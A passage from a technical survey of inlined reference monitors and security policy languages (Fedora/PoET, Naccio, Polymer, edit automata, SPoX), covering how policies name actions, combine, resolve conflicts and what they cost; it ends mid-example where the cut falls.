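Payette and Lagoze used PoET to control access to items in a digital library. They started with Fedora (unrelated to the Linux distribution), an architecture for digital repositories that they had helped develop at Cornell. A Fedora digital object contains related data, such as the video and slides of a lecture, and has methods for obtaining them. A book object might have one method for its table of contents and another for a single page. Java modules implement these methods, and several objects can share a module.

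Access rules for such objects can be very specific. One of Payette and Lagoze's lecture objects has this policy:

- Anyone may see the description and slides 1 to 10.
- Only users with Cornell credentials may see slides 11 to 20.
- The high-resolution video is available to users with Cornell credentials and to anyone who pays $5.

An operating system could restrict access to the underlying files, but its rules can't refer to slides or lectures. A single policy for the whole repository could include rules like these, but Payette and Lagoze expected it to become unmanageable as each object added its own. They instead stored each object's specific policy inside the object, as PSLang text. A separate default policy, which objects can share, covers the methods that all objects have and typically prevents ordinary users from changing an object's contents.

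PoET normally rewrites a program once, before it runs. Payette and Lagoze changed it to work on demand, so that a new version of a policy would take effect immediately. When a user makes a request, Fedora fetches the module that will handle it and sends the module to PoET with the object's policy. PoET inserts the checks and loads the result. The same module can therefore enforce different rules for different objects, which Payette and Lagoze demonstrated with objects from Cornell's computer science lecture archive. They left open what should happen when a repository's policy and an object's policy conflict.

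They had also hoped that an object could keep enforcing its policy after a user copied it to another device. Inlining alone cannot ensure this, because PoET protects its checks from the program that contains them, not from the computer's owner. A user who downloads an object controls the computer and, with enough knowledge of bytecode, can edit the class files to bypass the checks. Payette and Lagoze therefore proposed additional protection for objects that leave the repository, possibly with public-key cryptography or secured containers like IBM's Cryptolopes.

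## Naming what a policy controls: from Naccio to Polymer's abstract actions

A policy in SAL or PSLang refers to methods by name, so whoever writes it has to know every method that performs the act it controls. *A Language and System for Composing Security Policies* (Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, 2004) reports that Java's standard libraries contain a dozen or so methods that open a file. They include the constructors of `FileInputStream`, `RandomAccessFile` and `ZipFile`, and the methods that run an operating-system command, which can open any file, as an agent's shell tool can. A policy that lists these Java methods can't be reused for a Windows program, which doesn't have them.

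Naccio and Polymer both let a policy name an action, such as opening a file or fetching mail, rather than the methods that perform it. A separate mapping connects the action to those methods.

### Naccio's resources and platform interface

Evans and Twyman, in *Flexible Policy-Directed Code Safety* (1999), considered enforcing policies with wrappers, which are functions that perform a check and then call the original system function. They thought wrappers a reasonable way to enforce a policy but a poor way to write one. To limit how much a program writes to disk, the author would have to understand every system call that might write to a file, which in Java means dozens of methods. Naccio therefore generates the wrappers from three descriptions:

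- **Resource descriptions** list abstract operations, such as deleting a file or writing *n* bytes to it. They contain no checks, and informal documentation explains when each operation occurs.
- **The safety policy** attaches checks to these operations.
- **The platform interface** specifies which operations each system function performs, and with what values.

The platform interface contains most of the awkward details. Naccio has separate operations for creating a file and for overwriting one, but a Java program uses the same `FileOutputStream` constructor for both. The interface's code for that constructor tests whether the file exists, then calls the matching operation. The interface also links each Java file object to a Naccio object that identifies the file, so a policy can recognise the same file when the program reaches it through different Java objects.

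A policy generator combines the three descriptions and produces a modified copy of the platform's library, with wrappers only where the policy needs them. A second tool, the application transformer, makes the target use this copy. For many Java policies it only has to change the path where the virtual machine looks for classes.

*Policy-Directed Code Safety* (Evans, 1999) discusses where to place the platform interface. Placing it at the level of machine instructions would bring back SASI's difficulty in recognising file operations. Placing it at a high-level library such as Microsoft Foundation Classes would allow finer distinctions, such as between a file the user chose in a dialog box and one the program opened unprompted, but the policy would then work only for programs that use that library. Evans and Twyman chose the system's programming interface for both their prototypes, one for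 Java and one for Win32, the main Windows interface. At this level a policy cannot limit memory or processor time, because a program uses both without calling a system function.

The resource descriptions also limit what a policy can express. Naccio's write operation passes on the number of bytes but not the data, so a standard policy can restrict how much a program writes but not what it writes. A policy author can add such information by changing the platform interface, but must repeat the change on every platform.

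### Naccio's policies and their overhead

Evans and Twyman generated six policies for Java. The table gives the number of library methods Naccio wrapped for each policy and the time taken to generate it, in minutes and seconds.

| Policy | What it restricts | Methods wrapped | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Null | Nothing | 17 | 1:08 |
| LimitWrite | Changes to existing files, total bytes written | 30 | 1:59 |
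| LimitNetwork | Hosts, bandwidth, total data transferred | 31 | 2:12 |
| Paranoid | All of the above, plus windows, input events and threads | 130 | 5:08 |
| JavaApplet | Whatever the HotJava browser forbids applets | 114 | 5:51 |
| TarCustom | Actions that the archiving program tar should not need | 107 | 4:42 |

Every policy has to wrap the 17 methods in the first row, which protect class loading and reflection, so LimitWrite needs only 13 more.

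To measure the overhead, Evans and Twyman had a Java version of tar archive 10 MB in 3,152 files. Enforcing the JavaApplet policy with Naccio made the program 84% slower than with no checks, while enforcing it with Java's own security manager made it 153% slower. Naccio made most decisions before the program ran, and it stored each file's full path, which the security manager recomputed at every check. On a program that sent data over the network, Naccio was slightly slower than the security manager because it created objects to represent the connections.

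The overhead depends heavily on how often the program does what the policy restricts. LimitNetwork added almost no overhead to tar, which never uses the network, whereas Paranoid and TarCustom slowed it by slightly more than the security manager's 153%. These ratios come from a Java virtual machine without a just-in-time compiler, so they may not hold for compiled code.

The evidence for Naccio's portability is weaker. The measurements cover only the Java prototype, and the Win32 prototype had no protection against a program tampering with the checks.

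### Polymer's patterns and abstract actions

*Composing Security Policies with Polymer* (Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, 2005) describes a system whose policies are Java classes that respond to method calls. Polymer represents each call as an action object, which holds the method's signature, its arguments and the object on which the program called it. An action pattern selects actions by signature and can contain wildcards. For example, `<* java.lang.Runtime.exec(..)>` matches calls to `Runtime.exec` with any parameters and return type.

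The action declaration file lists patterns for all the methods that might affect security, and the rewriter inserts a call to the monitor in every method that matches one. A policy then uses its own patterns to determine which action has occurred.

Wildcards can group only methods with similar signatures, so Polymer also has abstract actions, which group methods by means of code. An abstract action's `matches` method receives a concrete action and returns true if the action belongs to the group. `GetMail`, for example, covers the methods that fetch email. Its `convertResult` method gives the policy an array of messages whichever method the program called:

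| Concrete method | What it returns | What `convertResult` returns |
|---|---|---|
| `IMAPFolder.getMessage` | One message | An array that contains the message |
| `IMAPFolder.fetch` | Nothing | The array of messages that the caller supplied |

A policy that logs incoming mail can therefore treat both methods alike. Abstract actions can make parameters uniform too. For example, `FileOpen` gives the policy a file name even for Java's `createNewFile` method, which takes no arguments. In that case, `FileOpen` gets the name from the file object the method was called on. Because `matches` can examine run-time values, an abstract action can also cover only some calls to a method, such as those that open files outside `/tmp`.

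Bauer and colleagues describe Naccio's mapping from methods to abstract events as many-to-one and Polymer's as many-to-many. In a many-to-one mapping, several methods can count as the same event, but each method counts as only one. A many-to-many mapping also allows one method to count as several events. For example, `IMAPFolder.getMessage` could belong to both `GetMail` and an abstract action for network use, so a mail policy and a network policy could each cover it.

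The practical difference is smaller than these labels suggest, and Bauer and colleagues call their design "slightly more general". The code in Naccio's platform interface can call more than one operation for a single method. Evans's later version also has overlapping groups of operations, so overwriting a file counts both as modifying an existing file and as modifying any file. Polymer's clearer advantage is that a policy's author can define a new abstract action in ordinary policy code, whereas a new Naccio operation requires a change to the platform interface.

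### Limiting the bytes a program writes

Suppose a policy allows a program to write at most one million bytes to disk. In simplified notation, a version that refers to concrete Java methods might look like this:

```
total = 0

before FileOutputStream.write(int b):                   count(1)
before FileOutputStream.write(byte[] b):                count(b.length)
before FileOutputStream.write(byte[] b, int i, int n):  count(n)
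...        // and the write methods of RandomAccessFile

count(n):
    if total + n > 1000000: stop the program
    total = total + n
```

The author needs to know some details of Java to get this right. The first method takes a four-byte integer but writes only one of its bytes. A `FileOutputStream` can also write to the screen instead of a file, in which case the policy should not count the bytes.

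With an abstract resource, the policy has one rule:

```
total = 0

before File.write(file, n):
    if total + n > 1000000: stop the program
    total = total + n
```

The list of methods and the details about integers and screen output move into the mapping, where other policies can use them.

Now suppose the platform gains a new way to write. Java 1.4, which Sun released in 2002, added `FileChannel`, a class with its own methods for writing to files. Until somebody updates the policy or the mapping, a program can write through `FileChannel` without changing `total`. The work needed depends on the design:

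| Design | What somebody must edit | What they must run again |
|---|---|---|
| Concrete methods | Every policy that restricts writing | The rewriter, on every target |
| Naccio | The platform interface | The policy generator, for every policy |
| Polymer | The abstract action, and the declaration file if no pattern covers the method | The rewriter, on the Java libraries |

The abstract version saves no work for a single policy, since somebody has to add the new methods either way. But if twenty policies restrict writing, it requires one edit instead of twenty.

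Some new methods require no edit. Naccio can let checking "pass through" a library method written in Java to the methods it calls. If a new method writes through `FileOutputStream`, the existing wrappers count the bytes. `FileChannel` would need its own wrapper because it reaches the disk through separate native methods, which are compiled for the machine instead of written in Java. In Polymer, a broad pattern such as `<* java.io.*.write(..)>` would cover a new `write` method in the `java.io` package once the rewriter had processed the updated library. The pattern would not match `FileChannel`, which is in a different package.

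### Who maintains the mapping

The people who build Naccio for a platform write its platform interface, and policy authors normally read only the resource descriptions. Writing the interface is a large job, since the standard resource descriptions contain 122 operations and Sun's version of Java 1.1.6 had 567 native methods. Pass-through checking reduces the work, but it ties the interface to one vendor's implementation, because another vendor might use a native method where Sun used Java code. Naccio's policy compiler warns about pass-through methods that depend on a native method without a wrapper.

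The University of Virginia's project page, *Policy-Directed Code Safety* (2000), gives its last update as 1 October 2000, more than a year before `FileChannel` appeared. Work on Naccio may have continued after that date, but an interface written for Java 1.1.6 cannot cover `FileChannel` unless somebody extends it.

Polymer gives more of this work to its users. *Policy Enforcement via Program Monitoring* (Ligatti 2006) lists six steps for programmers to secure an application, and the first is writing the action declaration file. Java generally cannot reload its library classes while a program is running, so a policy update during a run can control only methods already in the file. Programmers therefore have to anticipate later policies, and Bauer and colleagues advise them to write the file conservatively.

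Listing extra methods slows the program down. The rewriter took only 107 seconds to process all 28,742 methods in Java's standard packages, but each call to a listed method then transfers control to Polymer, even if the policy ignores the call. In a test that opened a network socket, this added about 0.62 milliseconds to an operation that took 36. With the same overhead on each write, a program that wrote a million bytes one at a time would take more than ten minutes longer.

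### Why errors in the mapping go unnoticed

A check runs only if the mapping connects the program's method to the policy's event. If the mapping omits `FileChannel`, writes through it go unchecked, with no error message, and harmless programs work as before. Reading the policy doesn't reveal the problem, because the rule is correct. The opposite mistake, counting a harmless method as a write, is easier to discover because it eventually stops a legitimate program and the user complains.

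Naccio's first vocabulary appears to have had a gap of this kind. In the 1999 paper, the property `NoOverwrite` is meant to protect every existing file, and it checks for overwriting, appending and deleting. But a program can also replace a file by renaming another file to its name, and the paper's file-system resource lists no operation for renaming. The property would not have prevented such a rename unless the platform interface treated it as a deletion. Evans's thesis adds two renaming operations and a group, `modifyExistingFile`, that includes them. Policies that use the group also cover any operation added to it later.

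A deliberate exception in the mapping can be dangerous too. Java's library has to read files and system settings to load a font. A platform interface could exempt these reads from checks, even when the program itself isn't allowed to read those files. Evans and Twyman warn against this because attackers had exploited font loading in some versions of Java to obtain restricted information. They recommend writing a wrapper for a method only when its effects on resources are completely certain.

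New kinds of resource raise a related problem. If somebody attaches a camera to the computer and adds a camera resource to Naccio, existing policies do not restrict it, because Naccio allows whatever a policy does not forbid. Evans knew that security designers usually recommend denying access by default, but he expected new resources to be fairly common and did not want to rewrite every policy for each one.

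The platform interface and the tools that process it, including an optimiser that removes unnecessary wrappers, are part of the trusted computing base. Evans thought a trusted base of this size might be acceptable where security needs were low or moderate, but not in security-critical systems. For those, he suggested combining Naccio with a simpler mechanism that enforces the most important properties.

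## Combining policies and resolving their conflicts: Polymer

Abstract actions let several policies refer to the same event, and those policies may specify different responses to it. Monitors that can only halt the target are easy to combine, because the program stops as soon as any of them detects a violation. Polymer's policies can also change a method's return value, run extra code or throw an exception, and two such responses to one call may be incompatible. Bauer and colleagues therefore treat each policy's response as a suggestion, which another policy can follow, override or merge with others.

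### Edit automata

Polymer is a practical form of the edit automaton, a state machine that can suppress a program's actions and insert new ones. Ligatti defines it by a set of states Q, an initial state q₀ and a transition function

δ: Q × A → Q × (A ∪ {·})

where A is the set of possible actions and · stands for no action. At each step the automaton reads the next action that the target wants to perform. It then either outputs an action of its own and leaves the target's action waiting (an insertion), or outputs nothing and discards the target's action (a suppression). Other responses combine these two. To accept an action, the automaton inserts a copy of it and then suppresses the original. To halt the target, it suppresses everything from then on.

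Ligatti's example is a cash machine whose software must log an amount, dispense it and then log that it has done so. Only complete transactions are valid. A halting monitor can't enforce this policy, because it would have to let the first log entry through and could not make the program finish the transaction. An edit automaton can hold the actions back until the transaction is complete:

| Step | The program attempts | The monitor outputs |
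|---|---|---|
| 1 | `logBegin(20)` | Nothing |
| 2 | `dispense(20)` | Nothing |
| 3 | `logEnd(20)` | `logBegin(20)`, `dispense(20)`, `logEnd(20)` |

The program continues after steps 1 and 2 as if its calls had succeeded. If it logged $20 and then tried to dispense $50, the monitor would halt the program, and neither action would take effect.

Ligatti proves that this technique can enforce any infinite renewal property, provided that the empty execution satisfies the property and a computer can decide whether a finite execution does. In an infinite renewal property, an infinite execution is valid exactly when infinitely many of its finite beginnings are valid. A cash machine that runs forever meets this condition if it keeps completing transactions. Every safety property is a renewal property, so edit automata can enforce more properties than halting monitors can.

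These monitors still can't enforce every policy. Suppose a program must eventually close every resource it opens. It might always open the next resource before closing the previous one. An infinite run would then obey the policy, but at least one resource would be open at every point after the first step, so the monitor would never have a valid sequence to release.

Suppression also works only if the monitor can convincingly simulate the action. Ligatti describes a policy that holds back writes to a file until the file contains a copyright notice. That policy must also intercept reads so that they reflect the pending writes. A monitor cannot simulate sending an email if the program waits for the reply, because the reply depends on somebody outside the system receiving the message. A monitor may also be unable to insert an action that needs a secret key it doesn't have. Even the cash-machine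 policy assumes that the reinserted calls complete normally. If the dispenser fails after the monitor has released the first log entry, the transaction remains incomplete.

### Separating decisions from effects

A Polymer policy has a `query` method, which receives an action and returns a suggestion. It can also have an `accept` method, which Polymer calls just before it follows the suggestion, and a `result` method, which receives the outcome afterwards. The `query` method should have no effects, such as changing variables, writing to files or displaying messages.

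Ligatti explains this separation with two policies that react to the same action. One prints an error message and halts the program, while the other prints an acceptance message and lets it continue. If both apply, the program should halt, but it's unclear which messages should appear. In Polymer, both policies make their suggestions without printing anything, and only the policy whose suggestion prevails prints its message. Earlier systems left this problem to the policy's author or settled it by the order of the policy text. Bauer and colleagues found no full specification of how Naccio combines the parts of a policy. Erlingsson's later policy language lets authors split a policy into several files, but it runs their effects in the order they appear in the combined text.

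The file-and-message policy shows why the separation also matters for a policy's memory. In Polymer it might look like this:

```
public class NoSendAfterRead extends Policy {
    private boolean hasRead = false;

    public Sug query(Action a) {        // decides, but changes nothing
        aswitch(a) {                    // selects a case by action pattern
            case <abs * FileRead()>:
                return new OKSug(this, a);
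            case <abs * Send()>:
                if (hasRead) return new ExnSug(this, a);
        }
        return new IrrSug(this);
    }

    public void accept(Sug s) {         // Polymer is about to follow s
        if (s.isOK()) hasRead = true;   // only a file read gets an OK
    }
}
```

If `query` set `hasRead` and a second policy refused the file read, the program would lose the right to send messages because of a read that never took place. The update is in `accept` instead, so the variable changes only when Polymer is about to allow the read.

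### The six suggestions

Each suggestion determines what happens to the target's call and which of the policy's other methods run:

| Suggestion | What happens to the call | `accept` | `result` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Irrelevant | It runs | No | No |
| OK | It runs | Yes | Yes, after the call |
| Insert | Another action runs first, then Polymer queries the policy again about the original call | Yes | Yes, after the inserted action |
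| Replace | It doesn't run, and the target receives a value from the policy | Yes | No |
| Exception | It doesn't run, and the target receives a security exception that it can catch | Yes | No |
| Halt | It doesn't run, and the target stops | Yes | No |

An insertion lets a policy gather information before it decides. For example, a policy can insert a dialog box, record the user's answer in `result`, and return "OK" or "exception" when Polymer queries it again.

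Polymer's 2004 version had only four suggestions: OK, suppress, insert and halt. The 2005 version split suppression into replacement and exception. With replacement, a program that reads an email's subject can receive an edited subject and continue normally, whereas an exception may interrupt the program. The 2005 version also added "irrelevant" for calls that a policy does not cover. This avoids unnecessary updates to the policy's state, and some ways of combining policies depend on whether a policy approved a call or the call was irrelevant to it.

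### Conjunction and conflicting replacements

A policy combinator is a policy that takes other policies as arguments and merges their decisions. Polymer's policies are ordinary Java objects, so a programmer can write a new combinator in the same way as any other policy. Bauer and colleagues found conjunction, which applies two policies at once, to be the most common. It ranks suggestions by how much they change the program's behaviour:

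irrelevant < OK < replace < exception < halt

If neither policy suggests an insertion, the combinator returns the least upper bound of their suggestions, which is the lowest suggestion that ranks at least as high as both. For "OK" and "halt", this is "halt". Two replacements with different values are incomparable because neither changes the program more than the other, so the combinator returns "exception", the lowest suggestion above both.

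For example, suppose one policy adds "SPAM:" to the subject of suspicious messages, and another shortens long subjects. Each replaces the return value of `getSubject`. For a suspicious message with a long subject, the two replacements differ, so the email program receives a security exception instead of a subject. This is safe because neither policy silently overrides the other. But the user probably wanted a subject with both changes, and conjunction can't apply one edit to the result of the other. Bauer and colleagues' own email policy avoids this conflict because a single component makes both changes.

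The combinator records which suggestions it used so that it can call `accept` and `result` only on the policies that made them. For example, suppose `NoSendAfterRead` approves a file read, but another policy replaces the file's contents with a redacted copy. Conjunction follows the replacement, so `NoSendAfterRead` receives no call, `hasRead` remains false, and the program can send the redacted text. (If the redacting policy reads the file through a monitored call, that call may still set `hasRead`.) Whether the program should be allowed to send the text depends on the purpose of the two policies and can't be determined from either policy's code alone.

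### How insertions make order matter

Conjunction handles insertions separately from the ranking. If either policy suggests an insertion, Polymer runs the inserted action and then queries both policies again about the original call. If both suggest insertions, Polymer runs the first policy's action first. Polymer also monitors inserted actions, so an insertion by one policy can change the other policy's state and next suggestion.

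Suppose a signature policy reads a signature file from disk before each outgoing message. A confirmation policy asks the user before a message goes out if the program has read a file since the last confirmation. The program has already read a file and now tries to send a message. The two possible orders have different results:

| Step | Signature policy first | Confirmation policy first |
|---|---|---|
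| 1 | Read the signature file | Ask the user |
| 2 | Ask the user | Read the signature file |
| 3 | Send the message | Ask the user again |
| 4 | – | Send the message |

In the second order, the confirmation policy treats the signature file as a new read, so the user has to answer twice. If only one of the policies inserted actions, their order would not affect the outcome, although the insertion could still change the other policy's decision.

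Polymer also runs insertions before it acts on refusals. If one policy suggests halting the program and the other suggests writing a backup first, Polymer writes the backup, queries both policies again and then halts the program. So a policy author can't assume that an inserted action runs only if Polymer eventually allows the original call.

### Giving one policy precedence

Conjunction doesn't suit policies that each permit a different activity. One component of the email policy allows only web connections and another allows only connections to mail servers, so their conjunction would refuse every connection. The `TryWith` combinator queries the first policy and uses the second only if the first rejects the action. `Dominates` follows the first policy whenever the action is relevant to it, and otherwise follows the second.

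| First policy's suggestion | `TryWith` | `Dominates` |
|---|---|---|
| Irrelevant | Follows the first | Follows the second |
| OK or insert | Follows the first | Follows the first |
| Replace, exception or halt | Follows the second | Follows the first |

`TryWith`, in the first row, can leave the second policy unenforced. Suppose the first policy allows only local network connections and the second limits the number of open files. When the program opens a file, the first policy returns "irrelevant". `TryWith` accepts that result, so the limit never applies. `Dominates` would pass the action to the second policy and enforce the limit.

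If no action is relevant to both policies, `Dominates` has the same effect as conjunction and is usually faster, because it often needs to query only the first policy. But if somebody later extends the first policy to cover an action that the second already restricts, `Dominates` will no longer enforce the second policy's restriction on that action.

### Selectors and modifiers

A selector enforces exactly one of its subpolicies. `IsClientSigned`, for example, applies a permissive policy to a cryptographically signed email program and a stricter one to any other. The 2004 report also describes selectors that delay their choice. One, for example, combines a policy that allows access to files and windows with a policy that allows access to the network and windows. The program can use windows freely, but once it does something that only one policy allows, the selector enforces that policy from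 then on, so a program that opens a file loses access to the network.

A modifier wraps a single policy and adds some behaviour to it:

- `Audit` returns the wrapped policy's suggestions unchanged and logs them along with the program's actions.
- `AutoUpdate` checks a remote site once a day for a new version of the policy, downloads it over a secure connection and loads it into the running virtual machine.
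- `Filter` hides certain actions from the wrapped policy.

`AutoUpdate` lets an administrator respond to a new attack without stopping the program, though only for methods already in the action declaration file. It also makes the remote site part of the trusted computing base, because whoever controls the site can replace the policy.

### Policies that monitor themselves

Polymer monitors security-relevant calls even when a policy makes them, which helps prevent confused deputy attacks but can also cause endless loops. If a policy responds to an action by inserting the same action, Polymer queries the policy about the inserted action, and the policy inserts it again.

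A loop can also begin inside `query`. The component that marks spam intercepts `getSubject` and then needs the original subject. If it gets this by calling `getSubject`, that call triggers another query, which makes the same call. A `Filter` can break such loops by hiding the repeated action. The email policy uses a more specific modifier, `QueryCalls`, which checks the call stack to determine whether the wrapped policy's `query` method made the call. If so, `QueryCalls` approves it without querying the policy again. This is an exception to complete mediation, so the policy author must be sure that the target can't use the `query` method to do something harmful.

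`QueryCalls` does not cover actions that a policy performs in `accept`, and Ligatti's cash-machine policy shows how easily an author can make a mistake there. When the transaction is complete, its `accept` method sets a flag to show that it is reinserting the suppressed calls, then makes them. But in the printed code, `query` never tests the flag. The reinserted `logBegin` would reach `query` in the middle of a transaction, and the policy would halt the machine's software before it dispensed any cash. The copyright-notice policy's `query` method does test a similar flag.

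### Securing an email client

Bauer and colleagues tested the design with a policy for email programs that use JavaMail, a standard Java library. They applied it to Pooka, a client with about 50,000 lines of source code, and did not need to inspect or modify that code. The policy has about 1,800 lines. One branch, which they include in all their larger policies, restricts class loading, reflection and operating-system commands and warns the user when memory is nearly exhausted. The other branch applies to email. Its main components are as follows:

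| Component | What it does |
|---|---|
| `ConfirmAndAllowOnlyHTTP` | Asks the user before each web connection and refuses other connections |
| `AllowOnlyMailPorts` | Allows connections only to the standard ports for mail servers |
| `Attachments` | Asks before the program creates a file of a dangerous type, such as .exe or .vbs |
| `OutgoingMail` | Logs messages, asks the user to confirm the recipients, sends a blind copy to a backup address and adds contact details |
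| `IncomingMail` | Logs messages, marks spam, shortens long subjects and warns about attachments |

`TryWith` joins the first two components, so the program can use the web and mail servers but nothing else. `OutgoingMail` opens a confirmation window that shows the user the recipients before a message goes out, as a defence against viruses like Melissa and the Love Bug.

The components vary in strength. `AllowOnlyMailPorts` checks the port number but not what the program sends, so a malicious client could send any data through a mail port to a server that the client's author controls. Ligatti considered encoding the mail protocols in the policy but decided that this would take too much programming effort and slow the program too much.

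The case study is good evidence that the combinators can express a realistic policy, since the email policy uses every kind of combinator. There is less evidence about how well the policy works, because Bauer and colleagues report extensive tests with Pooka but give no count of attacks blocked or legitimate actions refused. They designed both the language and the policy and did not compare the policy with one written as a single piece, so the study can't show how much effort the combinators save.

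### Costs

Polymer's rewriter took 107 seconds to process Java's standard packages, or about 3.7 milliseconds per method. It only has to do this once, because it inserts calls to a general policy manager instead of the policy's own code. Users can therefore change the policy without rewriting anything, but every monitored call must go through the manager.

Loading a class from the application took 12 milliseconds, twice as long as with Java's default loader, even when Polymer added no checks to it. When the rewriter modified every method in a class with 100 methods to add checks, loading took another 520 milliseconds.

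The 2004 report gives three times for opening a network socket:

| Configuration | Time |
|---|---|
| Without Polymer | 35.74 ms |
| Rewritten code, with a policy that covers no actions | 36.36 ms |
| Rewritten code, with a policy that allows everything | 38.64 ms |

The first two times differ by the 0.62 milliseconds mentioned earlier, which Bauer and colleagues call very low. That is low for a socket, but the simplest possible policy added another 2.28 milliseconds, for a total overhead of about 8%. Opening a file for writing takes only about one millisecond, so adding the same 2.9 milliseconds would make that take nearly four times as long. The later version may be faster, because it no longer checks each action against a list that the policy declares.

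The figure of 0.62 milliseconds is doubtful as a general measure of the overhead per call. It equals about 1.4 million clock cycles on the 2.2 GHz test machine, but the transfer requires only a couple of extra method calls. The real overhead may be much lower, with the rest due to variation between runs or to other work. Multiplying this figure by a large number of calls may therefore give an estimate that is far too high.

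Bauer and colleagues report that the email policy's delay was rarely noticeable, but they did not measure its overhead because Pooka spends much of its time waiting for the user. They also did not measure how overhead grows as a policy gains layers. Since conjunction queries both subpolicies about every action, a large policy could be much slower than the allow-everything policy in the socket test.

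### What the type-safety proof guarantees

Bauer and colleagues describe Polymer's behaviour formally in a small functional language with functions, memory, policies and suggestions. They prove that a well-typed program stays well-typed after each step, and that it can always take another step unless it has finished, halted or raised an uncaught exception. As in SASI's Java version, type safety protects the monitor from the target. The proof covers only this simplified language, not the bytecode rewriter or the Java virtual machine.

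The formal model also differs slightly from the implementation. Polymer calls `accept` before it halts a program, and one of the example policies uses that call to print a warning. In the model, the program halts without a call to `accept`. This does not affect type safety, but a policy can behave differently in Polymer than in the model.

A well-typed policy can still be wrong, and the proof does not rule out endless loops. An exception that a policy raises but doesn't catch passes into the target unless the policy's author adds a top-level policy to handle it. While Polymer creates the policy at start-up, it allows every action, so any file or network operation in the policy's initialisation code runs unchecked. Ligatti left the formal link between Polymer and edit automata for future work.

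The typing rules also do not require `query` to be free of effects. They require only that it take an action and return a suggestion, so a `query` method that changes a variable is still well-typed. An earlier language, from Bauer, Ligatti and Walker's *Types and Effects for Non-interfering Program Monitors*, was stricter. As Ligatti describes it, that language had a fixed set of combinators, and a static analysis could establish that the policies' effects would not conflict. Polymer lets programmers write any combinator, but they have to check for themselves that each `query` method only makes a decision.

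## Declarative policies: SPoX and ConSpec contracts

A Polymer policy can run any Java code, which makes it powerful but hard to check. Two later languages, SPoX and ConSpec, leave out most or all of this code. A policy in either language describes the sequences of actions that a program may perform, and a tool can analyse the description as an automaton. SPoX takes its way of naming events from aspect-oriented programming. ConSpec was designed to be simple enough for a phone to compare two policies automatically.

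### Aspect-oriented programming

Some requirements affect many parts of a program. If a program has to log every file operation, a programmer would normally add a logging call at each place where it uses a file. Aspect-oriented programming keeps the logging code and a description of those places in one unit, called an aspect. It relies on three concepts:

- A join point is a moment in a program's execution where extra code can run, such as a method call.
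- A pointcut is an expression that selects join points, such as all calls to the methods of `java.io.File`.
- Advice is the code that runs at the selected join points.

A tool called an aspect weaver inserts the advice into the program. AspectJ, a widely used aspect-oriented extension of Java, also has pointcuts that depend on the call stack. For example, its `cflow` operator can select file operations that occur while a particular method is still running.

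A security rewriter does much the same job as an aspect weaver. In a PSLang policy, the event acts as a pointcut and the code attached to it acts as advice. Hamlen and Jones describe Polymer as essentially an aspect weaver in *Aspect-Oriented In-lined Reference Monitors*, and Java-MOP, another monitoring system, runs on AspectJ. The thesis *Lightweight Inlined Reference Monitors for Securing Extensible and Open Systems* builds monitors for vehicle software and JavaScript using aspect-oriented programming, without a separate policy language. The main difference is that a security rewriter must also protect the added code from the program, while an ordinary weaver works on a program whose author wants that code.

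### What advice costs

Advice can do anything the language allows, so a reader who wants to know what an aspect enforces has to understand the advice, the target program and how they interact after weaving. Hamlen and Jones warn that the combined program can behave in surprising ways.

Advice also makes it unclear what to check the rewritten program against. Jones and Hamlen point out in *Enforcing IRM Security Policies* that policies with advice specify changes to code instead of properties of code. For example, a PSLang policy tells the rewriter to insert `hasRead = true` at a file read. If the policy's author forgets this line, the rewriter still does what the policy specifies, and there is no separate statement of the goal to expose the mistake. An automaton provides such a statement. A program either obeys it or doesn't, whichever tool produced the program, so a separate verifier could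 check the rewriter's output.

### SPoX: pointcuts on the edges of an automaton

SPoX (Security Policy XML) has pointcuts but no advice. A policy is a list of edges, and each edge has a pointcut and a change of state. The file-and-message policy looks like this:

```
<policy>
  <state name="s" />                   <!-- s starts at 0 -->
  <edge>                               <!-- a read moves s from 0 to 1 -->
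    <call>java.io.FileInputStream.read</call>
    <nodes var="s">0,1</nodes>
  </edge>
  <edge>                               <!-- a send in state 1 is a violation -->
    <call>java.net.SocketOutputStream.write</call>
    <nodes var="s">1,#</nodes>
  </edge>
</policy>
```

`#` marks a violation. In the formal definition of SPoX, as in SAL, an operation that matches no edge is also a violation. But the policies that Hamlen and Jones enforced on real programs list only a few events, so their prototype presumably allows all other operations.

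Pointcuts can select method calls, uses of a variable in an object, or individual bytecode instructions. They can also test a method's arguments, and a policy author can combine them with "and", "or" and "not". State variables hold integers. A policy can use a global variable to limit how many files the whole program opens, or an instance variable, which belongs to one object, to limit how many times the program reads each file object. A `forall` element stands for many similar edges. For example, a limit of 1,000 reads needs an automaton with 1,001 states, but the author writes a single edge from `i` to `i+1` and lets `i` run from 0 to 999.

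The rewriter adds a class that holds the state variables and places a check before each instruction. As in SASI, partial evaluation then removes the checks that can never affect enforcement. For a simple `forall`, the remaining check compares against the two ends of the range, without a loop. The prototype has about 4,000 lines of Java, excluding libraries.

Some SPoX policies cannot be enforced by inlining because the inserted check would itself violate the policy. Hamlen and Jones give the example of a policy that forbids the program's evaluation stack from holding more than one value. Even adding two numbers requires two values on the stack, so no useful check could run. The prototype guards against such cases by verifying that no instruction it inserts matches a pointcut in the policy.

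### SPoX on real programs

Hamlen and Jones first tried the prototype on RSSOwl, a news reader of about 5 MB. Their policy stopped the program from opening a network output stream after opening a file in the Windows directory. Rewriting took 17.6 seconds, about half of it for reading, unpacking and repacking files. They noticed no slowdown when they used the rewritten program.

One policy, designed as a worst case, counts every floating-point multiplication in SciMark, a set of numerical benchmarks. The rewritten benchmarks performed 76% fewer operations per second on average, so the same calculation took about four times as long. For policies on method calls, the overhead was too small to measure.

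In 2009, Jones and Hamlen published two case studies on existing Java applications. The first was Columba, an email client. Their policy forbids it to create or open .exe files, which can carry viruses. The rule takes four lines because it refers to a pointcut library, `fileMethods`, which lists the Java methods that access files. They found the number of such methods "surprisingly vast". These include methods that create databases, since a database is stored in a file whose name could end in .exe. Jones and Hamlen suggest that an expert should maintain the library so that other policy authors can reuse it, which resembles the division of labour in Naccio.

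Rewriting Columba took about 28 seconds and made the 2.8 MB program 3.6% larger. Columba is smaller than RSSOwl but took longer, probably because the library matches many more methods. Jones and Hamlen couldn't formally measure running times because Columba is interactive, but they noticed no delay.

The policy also forbids `Runtime.exec`, which starts other programs. This unexpectedly disabled Columba's spell-checker, which is a separate program. Jones and Hamlen show how to add an exception for trusted programs. They also acknowledge that they compiled the method library informally and that a closer study of Java would probably find omissions. The text pattern in the printed rule matches `.exe` anywhere in a name, so it would block a harmless file called `setup.exe.txt`.

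The other application was XNap, a file-sharing client. The policy stops users from taking files without offering any, by keeping downloads at most two ahead of uploads. In simplified notation, its 17 lines amount to this:

```
for every i from -2147483646 to 2:
    download:   i -> i+1
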